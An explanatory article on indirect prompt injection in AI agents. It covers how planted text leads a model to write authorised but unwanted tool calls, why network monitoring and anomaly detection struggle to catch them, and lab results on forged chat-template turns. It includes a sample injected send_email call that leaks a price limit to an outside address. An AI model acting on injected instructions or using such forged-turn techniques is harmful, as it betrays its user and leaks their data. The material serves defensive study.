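# Tool calls caused by injected text, and why network anomaly detection tends to miss them

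## How an AI agent turns text into an action under someone's account

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. The model only produces text, so to send an email or query a database it writes a tool call, a structured message (usually in JSON) that names a tool and gives its arguments. The software around the model, called the harness, builds the model's input, parses the call and executes it with the credentials of a user or a service account. A service account belongs to software and often serves many tasks at once.

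Anyone who can put text in front of the model can try to steer what the harness does. In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in a document, email or web page that the model will read while working for someone else. If the attack works, the model writes a tool call that its user never wanted, and the mail server or database receives a well-formed request from an account with permission to make it. Companies monitor their networks for intruders, mostly by looking for known malicious patterns or departures from normal traffic. Whether this monitoring can catch an injected call depends on what the call looks like from outside, which depends on how the agent makes it.

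### One cycle of an agent

Before the first cycle, the developer declares which tools exist. According to Anthropic's *Define tools*, each definition has a name, a plain-text description and an input schema, a machine-readable list of the arguments and their types. Anthropic's interface combines the definitions with the developer's instructions into a single system prompt, the text that opens the model's input. OpenAI's interface works similarly. According to *Function calling*, the definitions go into the system message and count as input tokens, the word fragments that a language model reads. The user's request comes after the system prompt, followed by whatever the agent has done and fetched so far. All of this forms one sequence of tokens. A chat template marks which parts came from the developer, the user or a tool, but the model has to learn from training to treat those parts differently.

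Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes the rest as a loop:

1. The harness sends the model the tool definitions and the user's message.
2. The model responds with one or more tool calls, and the response carries a flag that marks it as a request for tools.
3. The harness runs each tool and formats the output as a tool result.
4. The harness sends a new request that contains the original messages, the model's response and the tool results.
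5. The cycle repeats from step 2 until the model stops for some other reason, usually because it has written a final answer.

Anthropic writes that "the model never runs anything on its own." Microsoft's *Use the functions tool* describes the same arrangement, in which the model returns a structured call and the developer's code determines how and where the function runs. Each call has an identifier, which the harness copies into the result to match the two. A single response can hold several calls, so an unwanted call can appear alongside a wanted one.

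Outside text reaches the model in tool results. Under Anthropic's *Handle tool calls*, the developer returns the result in a message with the role "user", the role also used for the person's own request. OpenAI's interface has a separate type for tool output. In both, the text of a fetched email becomes part of the input the model uses to write its next call.

Anthropic runs its web search and page fetching tools on its own servers rather than on the developer's side, and one request may set off several searches before the customer's application receives anything. A sensor on the customer's network could record only the connection to Anthropic.

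*TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) describes how one-off connections between models and services became impractical as both multiplied, and developers moved towards the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024. An MCP client inside the harness sends a server the request `tools/list` and receives the names, descriptions and schemas of its tools. To use a tool, the client sends `tools/call` with a name and arguments, in the format set out in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026). The main software kits for the standard had close to half a billion downloads a month by July 2026, according to Model Context Protocol (2026). The version released that month also removed sessions. Each request now carries its own protocol version and client details, and any copy of the server can answer it. The protocol therefore has no session linking a call that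 sends an email to the earlier call in which the agent read one.

### The model writes the arguments, the harness supplies the authority

A server that protects its tools uses an access token to check whose authority a call is made under. This token is a string that stands for a set of permissions and is unrelated to the text tokens described above. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) requires the client to put an access token in the header of every HTTP request, while the tool's arguments go in the body. Servers that run on the same machine as the agent get their credentials from environment variables, which the operating system passes to a program. In both cases, the credential normally stays out of the model's input.

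Some servers without authentication, however, issue an identifier, such as one for a shopping basket, that anyone who has it can use. The model passes this identifier from call to call as an ordinary argument. An agent with a command-line tool may also be able to read environment variables that contain local credentials. But an attacker who wants an email sent only has to change the arguments, because the harness will attach the token to whatever call the model makes.

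The security company Quarkslab demonstrated this division with a medical assistant running on Claude 3 Haiku, a 2024 model. The application's login session held the patient's identity, while the model supplied only a patient number, and the tool fetched whichever record matched that number. A stricter system prompt blocked a user's direct request for someone else's record, but an instruction hidden in an uploaded web page still obtained it. Quarkslab fixed the tool by having it take the patient number from the session, or at least check the model's number against the session's. The company calls the flaw a confused deputy, an old term for a program tricked into using its authority for someone who lacks it. One purpose-built application is weak evidence of how common the flaw is, but it clearly shows which part of a request the model controls.

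Deployments differ in whose token the harness attaches, and there are three usual arrangements. The simplest is a shared service account. *mcps identity crisis when security theatre meets enterprise reality*, a blog post by the developer peteski22 (2025), collects configurations from official MCP servers. In the one for Grafana, a monitoring product, the server reads a service account token from an environment variable. Every task that goes through that server reaches Grafana under the same account, no matter who asked for it.

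Under the second arrangement, the user delegates access by logging in through a browser and approving the connection. The client then receives a token that identifies the user and allows it to act on their behalf (Model Context Protocol, 2025). GitHub's server in the same blog post takes a personal access token, which similarly makes the agent's work appear under the user's name.

The third possibility is to give the agent its own identity. The current Model Context Protocol specification allows for clients that act on their own behalf as well as clients that act for a user. A company can then give the agent fewer permissions than its users have and distinguish the agent's actions from people's in its logs. A dedicated agent identity is different from a service account shared by twenty unrelated scripts, although the procedure for getting the token can be identical.

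Combining these arrangements can also leave the user's identity out of a service's log. An MCP server must accept only tokens issued for itself and must not pass other tokens along, so it needs a second credential for the service behind it. According to peteski22, the June 2025 version of the protocol offered no standard way to obtain one, so developers used keys stored in configuration files instead. A request can therefore use the user's delegated token to reach the MCP server and a shared key to reach the service, in which case the service logs the shared account.

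Access tokens have limits, called scopes, such as permission to read files but not write them. A server can refuse a call that falls outside the token's scopes. But a scope usually covers a kind of operation, so permission to send email applies to strangers as well as colleagues unless the service adds its own rule.

Every call must also match the tool's schema. Anthropic's *Strict tool use* describes an option that restricts the model's output as the model writes it, so that the tool name is always a real one and the arguments always have the right types. For example, a booking tool that expects a whole number of passengers gets `2` rather than `"two"`. This prevents a lot of crashes, but it cannot establish where an argument came from, since an attacker's address is as valid a string as a colleague's. Without the strict option, a malformed call may still lead to a valid one, because the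 harness can return the error as a tool result, and Anthropic notes that Claude will then retry two or three times with corrections.

### Indirect prompt injection

The Frontier Model Forum, an industry body, divides prompt injection into direct attacks, in which the user types the malicious content, and indirect ones. NIST, the US standards institute, uses the term "agent hijacking" and treats it as the latest form of an old computer security problem, in which a system doesn't clearly separate trusted instructions from untrusted data.

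Yu, Cheng and Liu (2026), in *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing*, put the attack in a formula. Write *T* for the user's task, *M* for the model, *C* for each tool call and *O* for the result it returns. The attacker tampers with one result, which a prime marks, and the next call becomes

C′ₜ₊₁ = M(T, (C₁, O₁), …, (Cₜ, O′ₜ))

With the same task, model and earlier calls, one tampered tool result is enough to change the agent's next call. An injected call may be one the agent would not otherwise have made, or a wanted call with one argument changed. The formula describes a successful attack but does not give the success rate, which differs between models and can only be found by experiment.

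Yu and colleagues also point out that tools often return more than the agent needs. An agent that wants an email address may fetch a whole contact record, including a free-text comments field that could contain an injected instruction. A filter can reduce that risk by passing on only text in the form of an email address. The filter is of little use when the task is to summarise an email, because the model has to receive the whole body, including any injected text.

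### An example: the finance assistant

Suppose Dana, who buys office supplies for a company, asks her finance assistant to summarise the latest message from a paper supplier and email the summary to her colleague Luis. The assistant has two tools. `read_message` returns an email thread, and `send_email` takes a recipient and a body, both strings. The harness has a delegated token for Dana's mailbox. When a colleague forwarded the supplier's message to Dana, he added a note about the most the company would pay to renew the contract. The thread includes that note, and the supplier's message includes text that an attacker wrote for the model.

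The harness in this example sends mail without asking Dana first, which goes against the Model Context Protocol's advice. The protocol says that a person should always be able to refuse a call and that clients should show the arguments before sending them. The project's separate list of principles requires explicit consent before any tool runs, but states that the protocol itself cannot enforce this.

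The call that Dana wanted looks like this:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "luis@example.com",
    "body": "The supplier asks 45,000 euros to renew and wants a reply by Friday."
  }
}
```

The injected call looks like this:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "arguments": {
    "to": "desk@example.net",
    "body": "The buyers can go up to 52,000 euros to renew but aim to spend less."
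  }
}
```

Both calls satisfy the schema, and both use Dana's token, which permits her to send email. They also have the same number of characters. Real pairs would not match this closely, and an injected call that attached a year of invoices would be much larger than a two-line summary. But this attacker wants only one number, which fits in a short email.

The model might also write both calls, in which case Luis gets his summary and Dana has no reason to think anything went wrong.

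### What each observation point records

Four observation points, or places where someone records activity, are relevant to the example. We assume that the mail service offers its tools through a remote MCP server over an encrypted connection, and that its audit log stores recipients but not message text.

| Observation point | Wanted call | Injected call |
|---|---|---|
| Network sensor without decryption | An encrypted connection from the harness to the mail service: addresses, port, timing, sizes and handshake details | The same destination and sizes, with ordinary variation in timing |
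| Network sensor with decryption | Dana's token, headers with `tools/call` and `send_email`, and a JSON body with Luis's address and the summary | The same token and headers, and a JSON body with an outside address and the company's price limit |
| Mail service's audit log | Time, Dana's account, the client application, "message sent", a recipient inside the company | The same entries, with a recipient outside the company |
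| Harness trace | Dana's request, the supplier's message, the call and its result | The same request and message, followed by a call that does not fit the request |

The details in the first row are flow metadata, which a sensor can still record when it cannot decrypt a connection. Here they show only that the finance assistant contacted the mail service, which it does all day. The mail provider's servers then send the email to `example.net`, so if the company uses a cloud mail provider, that traffic never crosses the company's network.

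Decryption makes the whole request readable, but what a sensor can detect depends on which part it reads. Since July 2026 MCP clients have had to copy the method and the tool name into HTTP headers. Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) explains that this lets gateways and monitoring tools inspect a request without parsing its body. For Dana's assistant, those two headers have the same values in both calls. A server can also mark individual arguments for copying into headers, so a mail service could in principle expose the recipient there. However, the Model Context Protocol guidance advises against doing this with passwords, access tokens or personal data, and an email address is usually personal data. To tell the two calls apart, a gateway will therefore have to parse the JSON, and even then its only evidence will be an unfamiliar address and a sentence about euros.

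In this example, the audit log shows a different recipient for each call. But if Dana emails outside companies every day, as someone who buys supplies probably does, one more outside address is not unusual. The log also records both emails under Dana's name. If the finance assistant used a shared service account, the log would record them under that account instead, and nothing in the entries would connect them to Dana's request.

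Only the harness trace has everything in one place, and only if the harness stores message content as well as call names and times. The new version of MCP makes such records easier to assemble. The AI Alliance reports that OpenTelemetry, an open standard for recording what software does, is replacing the protocol's own logging, and mcp.directory's *MCP 2026-07-28* describes fixed fields that let a collector follow one request across several systems.

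Some companies will have fewer records to work with, because the prompts and the model's reasoning are often confidential. Liu and colleagues therefore designed their detector around what a gateway between the agent and its tools can record, which is the input, output and order of each call. For the finance assistant, such a gateway would hold the supplier's message and the outgoing email, but not Dana's request. An analyst could find the planted text but would have to guess whether Dana had wanted the supplier's contact to receive an email.

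Conventional monitoring tools work on the first three of these records and fall into a few types. Signature matching compares traffic or files with patterns from known attacks, such as a code string or a blacklisted address. Anomaly detection models normal activity, from past data or from assumptions, and raises an alert when something departs from it. For the injected call, the most likely departure is a recipient Dana has never written to before. Data loss prevention searches outgoing content for sensitive material, typically card numbers, personal records or documents with a confidentiality label. It needs access to the text of the email, and here that text is a sentence containing a price, much like the one Dana asked for.

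## The theoretical argument: why an authorised call leaves little to detect

Dana's two emails pass the same permission check because the mail service only compares each request with what her token allows, a weakness much older than AI agents.

### The confused deputy

Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells a lightly altered story from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Users who ran Tymshare's compiler could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also kept statistics about its own use in a system directory called SYSX, so Tymshare had given it permission to write to files there. The billing records were in SYSX too. One user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the debugging output file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission to write to SYSX, and the compiler overwrote the billing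 records.

The compiler wrote its output where the user asked, and the operating system applied its rule correctly, so no component had malfunctioned. Hardy traces the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources, the user who ran it and the company that installed it, with no way to state which one it was using for a given file. Tymshare first added a command that let the compiler choose between these two sources, but some programs turned out to need more than two. Hardy preferred capabilities, which are references that both identify a file and grant permission to use it. Under that system, the user would have needed a capability for the billing file to send the output there.

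Much of this applies to agents. The attacker cannot send mail from Dana's account but can supply text to a program that can. Quarkslab's medical assistant is especially close to Hardy's compiler, because the tool used the application's database access to fetch a record the patient had no right to read.

Dana's finance assistant, however, sends both emails under her token. It has only one authority to use, so a command for choosing between authorities would change nothing. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) explains that in the traditional problem it is unclear which principal (the person or organisation on whose behalf a program acts) the program is serving, whereas with an agent it is unclear what the principal intended.

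This also makes capabilities less effective. The injected call would fail if Dana gave the assistant a capability to email only Luis, but she would have to know the recipients before the task starts. If she asks the assistant to reply to whoever in the thread handles the contract, the address has to come from the thread, where the attacker can plant one.

Injected calls can pass even strong identity checks. In *After the identity fix*, a 2026 SC Media commentary, the engineer Nik Kale imagines a user asking an agent to summarise a PDF. Hidden instructions in the file make the agent change a customer's email address and trigger a password reset. Every credential in the example is valid, short-lived and narrowly scoped. Identity controls can establish who the agent is, what it may access and whose authority it is using, but not whether the user asked for the action. They are still useful because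 a narrower scope limits what an injected call can do. Detecting calls within that scope requires some other sign that they are out of place.

### Does misuse look abnormal?

Anomaly detection assumes that misuse looks different from normal use. Dorothy Denning's *An Intrusion-Detection Model* (1987), an early and influential design, rests on the hypothesis that security violations show up as abnormal patterns in a system's audit records. Her system would build a statistical profile of each user's activity and flag departures from it. In one of her examples, a legitimate user who leaks documents might log in at unusual hours or send data to a printer they don't normally use.

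In *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), Axelsson writes that anomaly detection has the potential to catch abuses of legitimate privileges that are hard to write into a security policy. Detecting injected calls would need exactly this ability.

But an injected call can look ordinary. A thief who steals Dana's password will probably use a different computer, keep different hours and open different files, whereas an injected call comes from her usual harness while she is working. In *Mimicry Attacks on Host-Based Intrusion Detection Systems* (2002), Wagner and Soto showed that attackers can disguise an intrusion as normal behaviour, and defeated a published detector this way. With an agent, the harness provides part of the disguise by formatting and sending the attacker's call like any other.

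Harmless activity can also look strange. Robin Sommer and Vern Paxson, in *Outside the Closed World* (2010), argued that machine learning is better at recognising things similar to what it has seen before than at finding meaningful outliers. Network traffic varies so much that it is hard to learn a stable idea of "normal". They also described a semantic gap, in which a detector reports that something is unusual but the operator needs to know whether it is an attack.

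*Blind to What They Can Fix* (2026) measured an example of this gap in a very different setting. AI coding agents wrote programs to play the video game Seaquest, and the researchers then changed the game in 25 ways. A general monitor compared the programs' behaviour with earlier normal runs. It raised an alarm in 97% of the cases where a program failed, but also in 73% of the cases where the game had changed and the program still worked. An office agent encounters harmless changes all the time, such as its user taking on a new client.

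The objection is weaker for an agent with one narrow job. If an agent sends the same report to the same three people every night, a fourth recipient is a good reason for an alert. Sommer and Paxson themselves advised keeping a detector's scope narrow. Dana's assistant is a much harder case because it does whatever she asks.

### A limit on any detector

A standard result in statistics makes the argument more precise. A detector receives a record *z* of each call, which might be a size and a time for a network sensor, or the whole request for a gateway that decrypts traffic. Let *P*₀ be the probability distribution of *z* over benign calls and *P*₁ its distribution over injected calls. The detector is defined by the set *A* of records that trigger an alert. Its false positive rate is *P*₀(*A*) and its recall is *P*₁(*A*).

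The total variation distance between the two distributions is the largest gap between the probabilities they give to any one set of records:

TV(P₁, P₀) = max over all sets S of |P₁(S) − P₀(S)|

The distance is 0 when the distributions are identical and 1 when they have no records in common. Since *A* is one of the sets that the maximum covers, it follows that

recall − false positive rate = P₁(A) − P₀(A) ≤ TV(P₁, P₀)

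The limit also applies to a detector that makes some of its decisions at random, because such a detector is an average over such sets. *Blind to What They Can Fix* uses the same inequality and notes that it covers everything the monitor receives, including its reference data on normal behaviour.

If the distance is 0.05, for example, and a company accepts a false positive rate of 0.1%, recall cannot exceed 5.1%. The limit comes from the records, so a better algorithm cannot raise it. At a distance of zero, a detector does no better than raising alerts at random. The true distance depends on the account, on what the observation point records and on the attacker, who can choose calls that make it smaller.

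At low false positive rates, the limit can be far higher than the recall any detector can achieve. Suppose a log records only whether each recipient is inside or outside the company, and that 30% of Dana's wanted emails and all the injected ones go outside. The distance is then 0.7. A detector that flags every outside email reaches the limit exactly, with 100% recall and a 30% false positive rate, but the company would soon switch it off. To bring the false positive rate down to 0.1%, the detector can flag only one in 300 outside emails, chosen at random. Its recall then falls to 0.33%, although the formula allows 70.1%.

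*Closed-Form Noise Calibration Against Membership Inference for Random-Allocation DP-SGD* (2026) shows a similar gap in privacy research, for tests of whether a particular record was in a model's training data. At a false positive rate of 0.1%, the best possible test had a recall of 0.22% to 0.24%, while the total variation limit was 10.1%. A detector that must rarely raise a false alert needs features that almost never occur in benign calls. For 90% recall at a 0.1% false positive rate, the records that trigger alerts must be 900 times as common among injected calls as among benign ones.

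A run of calls may be easier to detect than a single call. *Stronger Judges Do Not See More* (2026), a paper on detecting tampering with AI systems from their outputs, proves that the distance over *N* independent observations is at most *N* times the distance for one. Ten calls at 0.05 each could therefore reach 0.5 at most, though a distance of exactly zero stays zero over any number of calls. Looking at calls together helps against an attacker who steers an agent for a week, but much less against one injected email among a hundred wanted ones, because the proof assumes that either every observation in a run comes from a tampered system or none does.

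### What recording more can do

Adding fields to a record can increase the distance but never reduce it, because a detector can ignore the added fields and use any alert rule that worked on the shorter record.

A detector could also examine a call's arguments. *Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* (2026) describes a detector that ignored them and flagged agents that retrieved something from memory and then sent an email. An attacker stealing stored data through email has to produce this sequence, but an agent that looks up a deadline and emails its team produces it too. The false positive rate on such harmless work reached 57.6% in one setting. The two cases differ only in the recipient's address, which the detector excluded by design.

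In Dana's case, the most useful addition to the record would be her request. She asked for an email to Luis, so a record that contains both the request and the recipient separates the two calls almost completely. Kale, in SC Media, proposes a similar check, in which the software around the model signs a digest of the user's request and the operation it calls for, and each tool refuses a call that doesn't match. If the declared operation is just `send_email`, both of the assistant's calls match. If it includes Luis's address, only the wanted call matches, but then something has to extract the address from Dana's request without being influenced by the supplier's message.

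A record could also include the source of each argument. Lan and colleagues suggest, but do not test, labelling web content as untrusted when it enters the system and passing the label on to any argument it influences. In Dana's case, the label would distinguish the two addresses, because the one in the wanted email comes from her request and the one in the injected email comes from the supplier's message. The label would not help with the body, because a summary of an untrusted message always derives from untrusted text. Working out which text influenced an argument is also difficult, since the model processes all its input together.

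An extra field helps only if it is related to the difference between benign and injected calls. In the Seaquest experiments in *Blind to What They Can Fix*, the checks that the programs' authors had written missed 52% of failures. Adding related evidence cut this to 3.7%, while unrelated evidence left it at 50%. A detector can still perform badly with good records. In the same game, a learned anomaly detector missed 52% of failures, while the general monitor missed only 3% using the same statistics.

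### Rare attacks and false alerts

Even a detector with high recall can be useless if attacks are rare. Bayes' theorem gives the share of alerts that are real. If π is the share of calls that are injected, then

share of alerts that are real = (π × recall) / (π × recall + (1 − π) × false positive rate)

Suppose a company's agents make one million calls a day, of which ten are injected, and its detector has a recall of 90%. It catches nine injected calls a day. The number of false alerts depends on the other 999,990 calls:

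| False positive rate | True alerts a day | False alerts a day | Share of alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 9 | about 10,000 | 0.09% |
| 0.1% | 9 | about 1,000 | 0.9% |
| 0.01% | 9 | about 100 | 8% |
| 0.001% | 9 | about 10 | 47% |

At a false positive rate of 0.1%, which would be excellent in many other fields, an analyst has to go through about 112 alerts to find one real attack. If the total variation distance were also 0.05, the detector would catch at most one injected call every two days, while still raising a thousand false alerts a day.

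Axelsson made this argument about ordinary computer networks. He imagined a small site that produces a million audit records a day and suffers two intrusions, each affecting ten records. If a detector flagged all 20 of those records and had a false positive rate of 0.001%, two thirds of its alerts would be real. At a rate of 0.1%, only about 2% would be real. Axelsson knew of no experiments on how security staff respond to false alarms, so he relied on research on operators in settings such as power stations and paper mills. That research suggested that most people would lose faith in an alarm well before half its alerts were false.

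Researchers who test detectors for agents have started to account for how rare injections are. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) measures how many injections detectors catch at a false positive rate of 1%, because a detector that screens every tool output will process far more benign outputs than injected ones. That rate is stricter than in much testing, but a detector screening a million outputs a day would still raise about 10,000 false alerts.

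The result depends on the assumptions, and ten injected calls in a million is a guess. A company can also raise the share of alerts that are true by checking fewer calls, such as only those that send something outside the company after the agent has read outside text. If 10,000 calls a day qualify and all ten injected calls are among them, the same recall and false positive rate would give nine true alerts and about ten false ones, which one analyst could handle. However, benign calls in this group resemble injected ones more than most calls do, so the false positive rate would probably be higher than 0.1%. The company would also miss injected calls that send nothing outside.

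Axelsson acknowledges that his assumptions fit anomaly detection less well when it is used to find stolen identities, because an intruder who takes over an account may affect many more records. An injected call often affects only a few. Dana's assistant needs to send only one unwanted email for the attacker to learn the company's price limit.

### New destinations and approved services

Injected calls can sometimes be distinguished from wanted ones, because the attacker's goal may require a call that is unusual for the account. Someone stealing data has to send it somewhere they can read it, which may be an address the agent has never contacted. Stealing a large amount of data also takes either one very big call or many small ones.

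Lan and colleagues tested an attack that could be recognised by its destination. Their agent, which ran on a small open model, had to summarise a web page containing instructions to send private data to the attacker's server. An allowlist, which permits requests only to named domains, blocked the request in all 30 runs. In 120 separate runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server. The experiment favoured the allowlist, because the researchers chose a domain clearly outside it and summarising a page requires no contact with unknown servers. An agent that does research on the web routinely opens unfamiliar sites. Lan and colleagues also warn that attackers can move data through trusted sites.

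Whether a destination counts as new depends on where the traffic is observed. In Dana's case, a rule that flags new recipients can use the mail service's audit log, but not a network sensor without decryption. In *When Agents Look Like Beacons*, Sohail (2026) similarly argues that when an attacker manipulates an agent into misusing legitimate tools, the threat is in the content of the traffic, which has the same structure as benign traffic.

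Other injected calls take effect entirely within approved services, so the agent contacts no new server and writes to no new recipient. The password reset in Kale's example is one, at least until the service sends the reset email. An agent with access to an accounting system could change a supplier's bank details, so that the company's next routine payment goes to the attacker. An agent could also copy a confidential file into a shared folder that the attacker, perhaps a contractor, can already read.

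Volume and sequence can still expose some of these calls. An agent that normally edits five records a day and suddenly deletes 4,000 will stand out in any reasonable audit log. But a single change of bank details is a normal event in an accounting system, and a customer who has changed their email address may well reset their password next. Detecting the injected version would require evidence that nobody had asked for the change, which the accounting system's log doesn't contain.

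For calls like these, Kale recommends a separate confirmation step. The agent could prepare a change of address but not complete it. A second tool would check the draft against the state of the session and could ask a person to approve it. This can stop an injected call even if no detector flags it as unusual. However, changes the user wants have to go through the same step, and a person who approves dozens of changes a day may stop reading them.

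## Laboratory experiments on making models issue injected calls

An injected call reaches a service only if the model writes it, so the number of calls that monitoring has to catch depends on how well models resist injections. Researchers measure this resistance by giving an agent a harmless task, planting an instruction in one of its tool results and checking whether the agent carries it out. The attack success rate is the share of test cases in which it does. Published rates for 2026 models range from zero to more than 90%, because they depend heavily on the attack, the kind of task and how many tries the attacker gets.

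### Three outcomes of an injection

In *CounterSteer*, Russinovich (2026) distinguishes three effects an injection can have. In a tool hijack, the agent calls a tool the attacker chose, with content the attacker chose. In parameter manipulation, the agent calls the tool the task requires but puts the attacker's content in one of its arguments. In contamination, injected text leaks into a legitimate call the attacker was not targeting. Russinovich counts the first two as compromises and records contamination without counting it as one.

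Dana's assistant could produce all three. If it also had a tool for creating mail-forwarding rules and the supplier's message made it use that tool, that would be a tool hijack. Sending the email for Luis to `desk@example.net` would be parameter manipulation. If the assistant ignored the planted instruction but copied a sentence of it into Luis's summary, that would be contamination.

Parameter manipulation is the hardest of these attacks to see from outside. A tool hijack usually adds a call, which may be of a type Dana's account has never made before, and a gateway that reads only the tool's name could notice it. With parameter manipulation, the number of calls, their order, the tool names and the services contacted can all match a normal run. A detector has to read the argument and compare it with some estimate of what it should have been. An unfamiliar recipient is a weak clue, but a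 changed payment amount or booking date may look as ordinary as the value it replaced. Contamination adds no call either, but the attacker doesn't control where the text ends up.

Russinovich tested five open-weight models, whose weights anyone can download, by placing injections in real tool records and in Wikipedia pages. Without a defence, parameter manipulation through web pages succeeded in 81% to 100% of cases on the models where he measured it. The document format mattered a lot for one model, Gemma-4-31B, which followed 87% to 100% of the injections in web pages but only 5% to 11% of those in JSON records.

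He also used AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents carry out tasks in simulated workplace applications. Without a defence, between 10% and 49% of the attacks succeeded. Llama-3.1-8B had the lowest rate, but it could complete only about a quarter of the ordinary tasks, so its apparent resistance may be partly due to being bad at using tools.

Russinovich's defence, also called CounterSteer, measures how the model's internal state differs between following an embedded instruction and ignoring one, then subtracts that difference wherever the model reads a tool result. This cut the AgentDojo rates to between 0.6% and 7.9%. He then tried 24 wordings of each injection against gpt-oss-20b with the defence in place. At least one wording worked in 3 of 18 tool-hijack cases and 13 of 18 parameter-manipulation cases.

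To find out why, he trained simple classifiers to predict from the model's internal state whether it would follow an injection. For parameter manipulation, the classifiers scored only 0.53 at the injected text, on a scale where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. They scored 0.82 to 0.90 once the model was writing the argument, but by then it had typically quoted the injected sentence in its own reasoning and adopted it. So even someone who can inspect the model's internals may get little warning before the call. SecAlign, a defence that retrains the model, failed in only 1 of the 18 cases, though its training had included the same families of wording.

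Russinovich excludes cases where the user tells the agent to do whatever a document says. If Dana asks her assistant to handle everything in the supplier's message, her instructions arguably cover an injected request too. Users gave this kind of instruction in 36 of the 180 AgentDojo episodes he used, and every attack that still worked on the defended gpt-oss-20b occurred in those 36. A record of the user's request is much less useful in such cases, because the request does not specify what the call should contain. In the benchmark's banking tasks, the text that worked best against the defences was a false item on a bill, which contains no instruction.

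### Chat templates and forged turns

A chat template shows the model who wrote each part of its input. It puts a marker at the start of each turn, followed by a role name (system, user, assistant or tool), and another marker at the end. Many templates also have markers for the model's reasoning and its tool calls. Each family of models has its own template, which developers publish for open models but usually not for closed ones.

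Developers train models to give the system prompt the most authority, followed by the user, the assistant's own earlier turns and finally tool output. The model should therefore follow Dana's request over an instruction in an email. But the model relies on the markers to distinguish these roles, and the markers sit in the same sequence of tokens as the text they separate. Deng, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *Automating Agent Hijacking via Structural Template Injection*, identify this as the underlying weakness. Templates give the conversation a logical structure, but they do not strictly isolate control instructions from untrusted data.

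An attacker can exploit this with a forged turn, which is text that imitates the end of a tool result and the start of a new user or system turn. The harness places this text inside a genuine tool result, as it would any other text. The model may read the tool result as ending early and being followed by a new request from the user. If the model acts on that request, it writes a real tool call and the harness executes it.

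Attackers can also imitate a tool-call segment. The harness looks for tool calls only in the model's output, so it will not execute the imitation, but the model may read it and continue as though it had already decided to use a tool. The resulting call has the same format as any other, so it carries no sign of the forgery for the network or the receiving service to detect.

The software that turns text into tokens determines how the model receives an imitated marker. Genuine markers are usually control tokens, single entries in the model's vocabulary that ordinary writing should never produce. If the software handles tool results carelessly, a marker spelled out in an email turns into the real control token, and the model receives the same input as it would at a genuine turn boundary. This is a conventional software bug, fixed by encoding outside text so that it can never produce a control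 token. The fix belongs in the harness or, for a hosted model, on the provider's servers.

After that fix, the same email reaches the model as ordinary tokens that spell out the marker. The model could in principle distinguish this text from a real boundary, but may still treat it as one because the two look so similar. Solving this takes training or a filter that recognises imitations of the marker, which can take many forms. Better encoding cannot help, because the text is already encoded correctly.

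### ChatInject

*ChatInject* (Chang, Jun and Lee, 2025) measures how much forged chat turns add to the success rate of an ordinary injection. The attacker controls a tool result but knows neither the user's request nor the system prompt. The plain version is an attention-grabbing sentence followed by an instruction. The forged version puts the same sentence in an imitation system turn and the same instruction in an imitation user turn. An attack succeeds only if the agent completes every step of the injected task.

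Chang and colleagues ran both versions on two benchmarks. InjecAgent gives the agent a prepared tool result containing an injection meant to cause direct harm or steal data. AgentDojo lets the agent work through a whole task, and its code checks whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it completed the attacker's. They used AgentDojo's Slack, travel and banking applications. They tested nine models available in 2025, six with public templates and three closed ones.

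Across the six open models, plain-text attacks succeeded in 5.18% of AgentDojo cases on average, compared with 32.05% for forged turns. On InjecAgent, the averages were 15.13% for plain text and 45.90% for forged turns. A single model accounts for much of the plain-text average on InjecAgent. Llama-4 followed 50.1% of those injections, while the other five averaged about 8%. The AgentDojo results for each model, as attack success rates in percent, were:

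| Model | Plain text | Forged turn | Forged turn with imitation tool call |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen-3 | 17.5 | 54.8 | 69.4 |
| GPT-oss | 0.3 | 51.4 | 47.4 |
| Kimi-K2 | 5.9 | 29.3 | 44.2 |
| GLM-4.5 | 0.3 | 20.3 | 36.0 |
| Grok-2 | 6.1 | 19.3 | not tested |
| Llama-4 | 1.0 | 17.2 | 19.8 |

The imitation tool call helped the attacker on four of the five models that have a marker for it, even though the AgentDojo version did not name a real tool. The exception was GPT-oss, which was already very vulnerable to forged turns; adding the call lowered the rate slightly. But on InjecAgent, adding it raised GPT-oss's rate from 14.2% to 19.1%, so the exception may not mean much.

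Grok-2's template has only a light separator between turns and no tool-call marker to imitate. On InjecAgent, a forged turn raised its rate only slightly, from 16.5% to 17.7%. Chang and colleagues take this as evidence that forged turns get their authority from clear role markers. That is plausible, but a forged turn still tripled Grok-2's rate on AgentDojo, and one model with an unusual template is not enough to confirm the explanation.

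The attacks often disrupted the user's own task too. On AgentDojo, Kimi-K2 completed 71.5% of user tasks under plain-text attack but only 35.0% when the attacks used forged turns. Some users would notice the failure, though they might well assume it was an ordinary mistake.

Chang and colleagues also attacked each model with other models' templates, which bears on whether a model needs to receive a real control token. GLM-4.5's own template succeeded against it in 20.3% of AgentDojo cases, and no other template exceeded 3.3%. By contrast, Qwen-3's template raised the success rate on the closed model GPT-4o from 6.4% to 27.3%, and on Grok-3 from 8.2% to 33.2%. Gemini 2.5 Pro fell in between, with five of the seven borrowed templates doing worse than plain text. These results suggest that some models respond to text that merely resembles their markers, although the templates of closed models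 are secret, so a borrowed marker might match a real one.

The researchers also altered some of the characters in each template at random. The altered templates still worked better than plain text on all three models they tested. A marker with a wrong character should not become a control token, so this result is fairly good evidence that ordinary text can act as a marker, although the random changes may have left some markers intact. The result also limits signature matching. A sensor that can read incoming documents could search for exact copies of known markers, but an attacker can avoid an exact match by changing some characters.

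### How much of the effect comes from the forged turn?

A later paper, *Will the User Ever Know?* (Lee, Kim and Lee, 2026), compares ChatInject on AgentDojo with an older plain-text attack that poses as an urgent message from the user. The older attack succeeded more often on two of the three models where they could be compared, with rates of 37.6% against ChatInject's 17.1% on Qwen3-235B and 19.6% against 17.5% on GPT-4o-mini. ChatInject succeeded more often on Llama-3.3-70B, at 32.1% against 22.0%.

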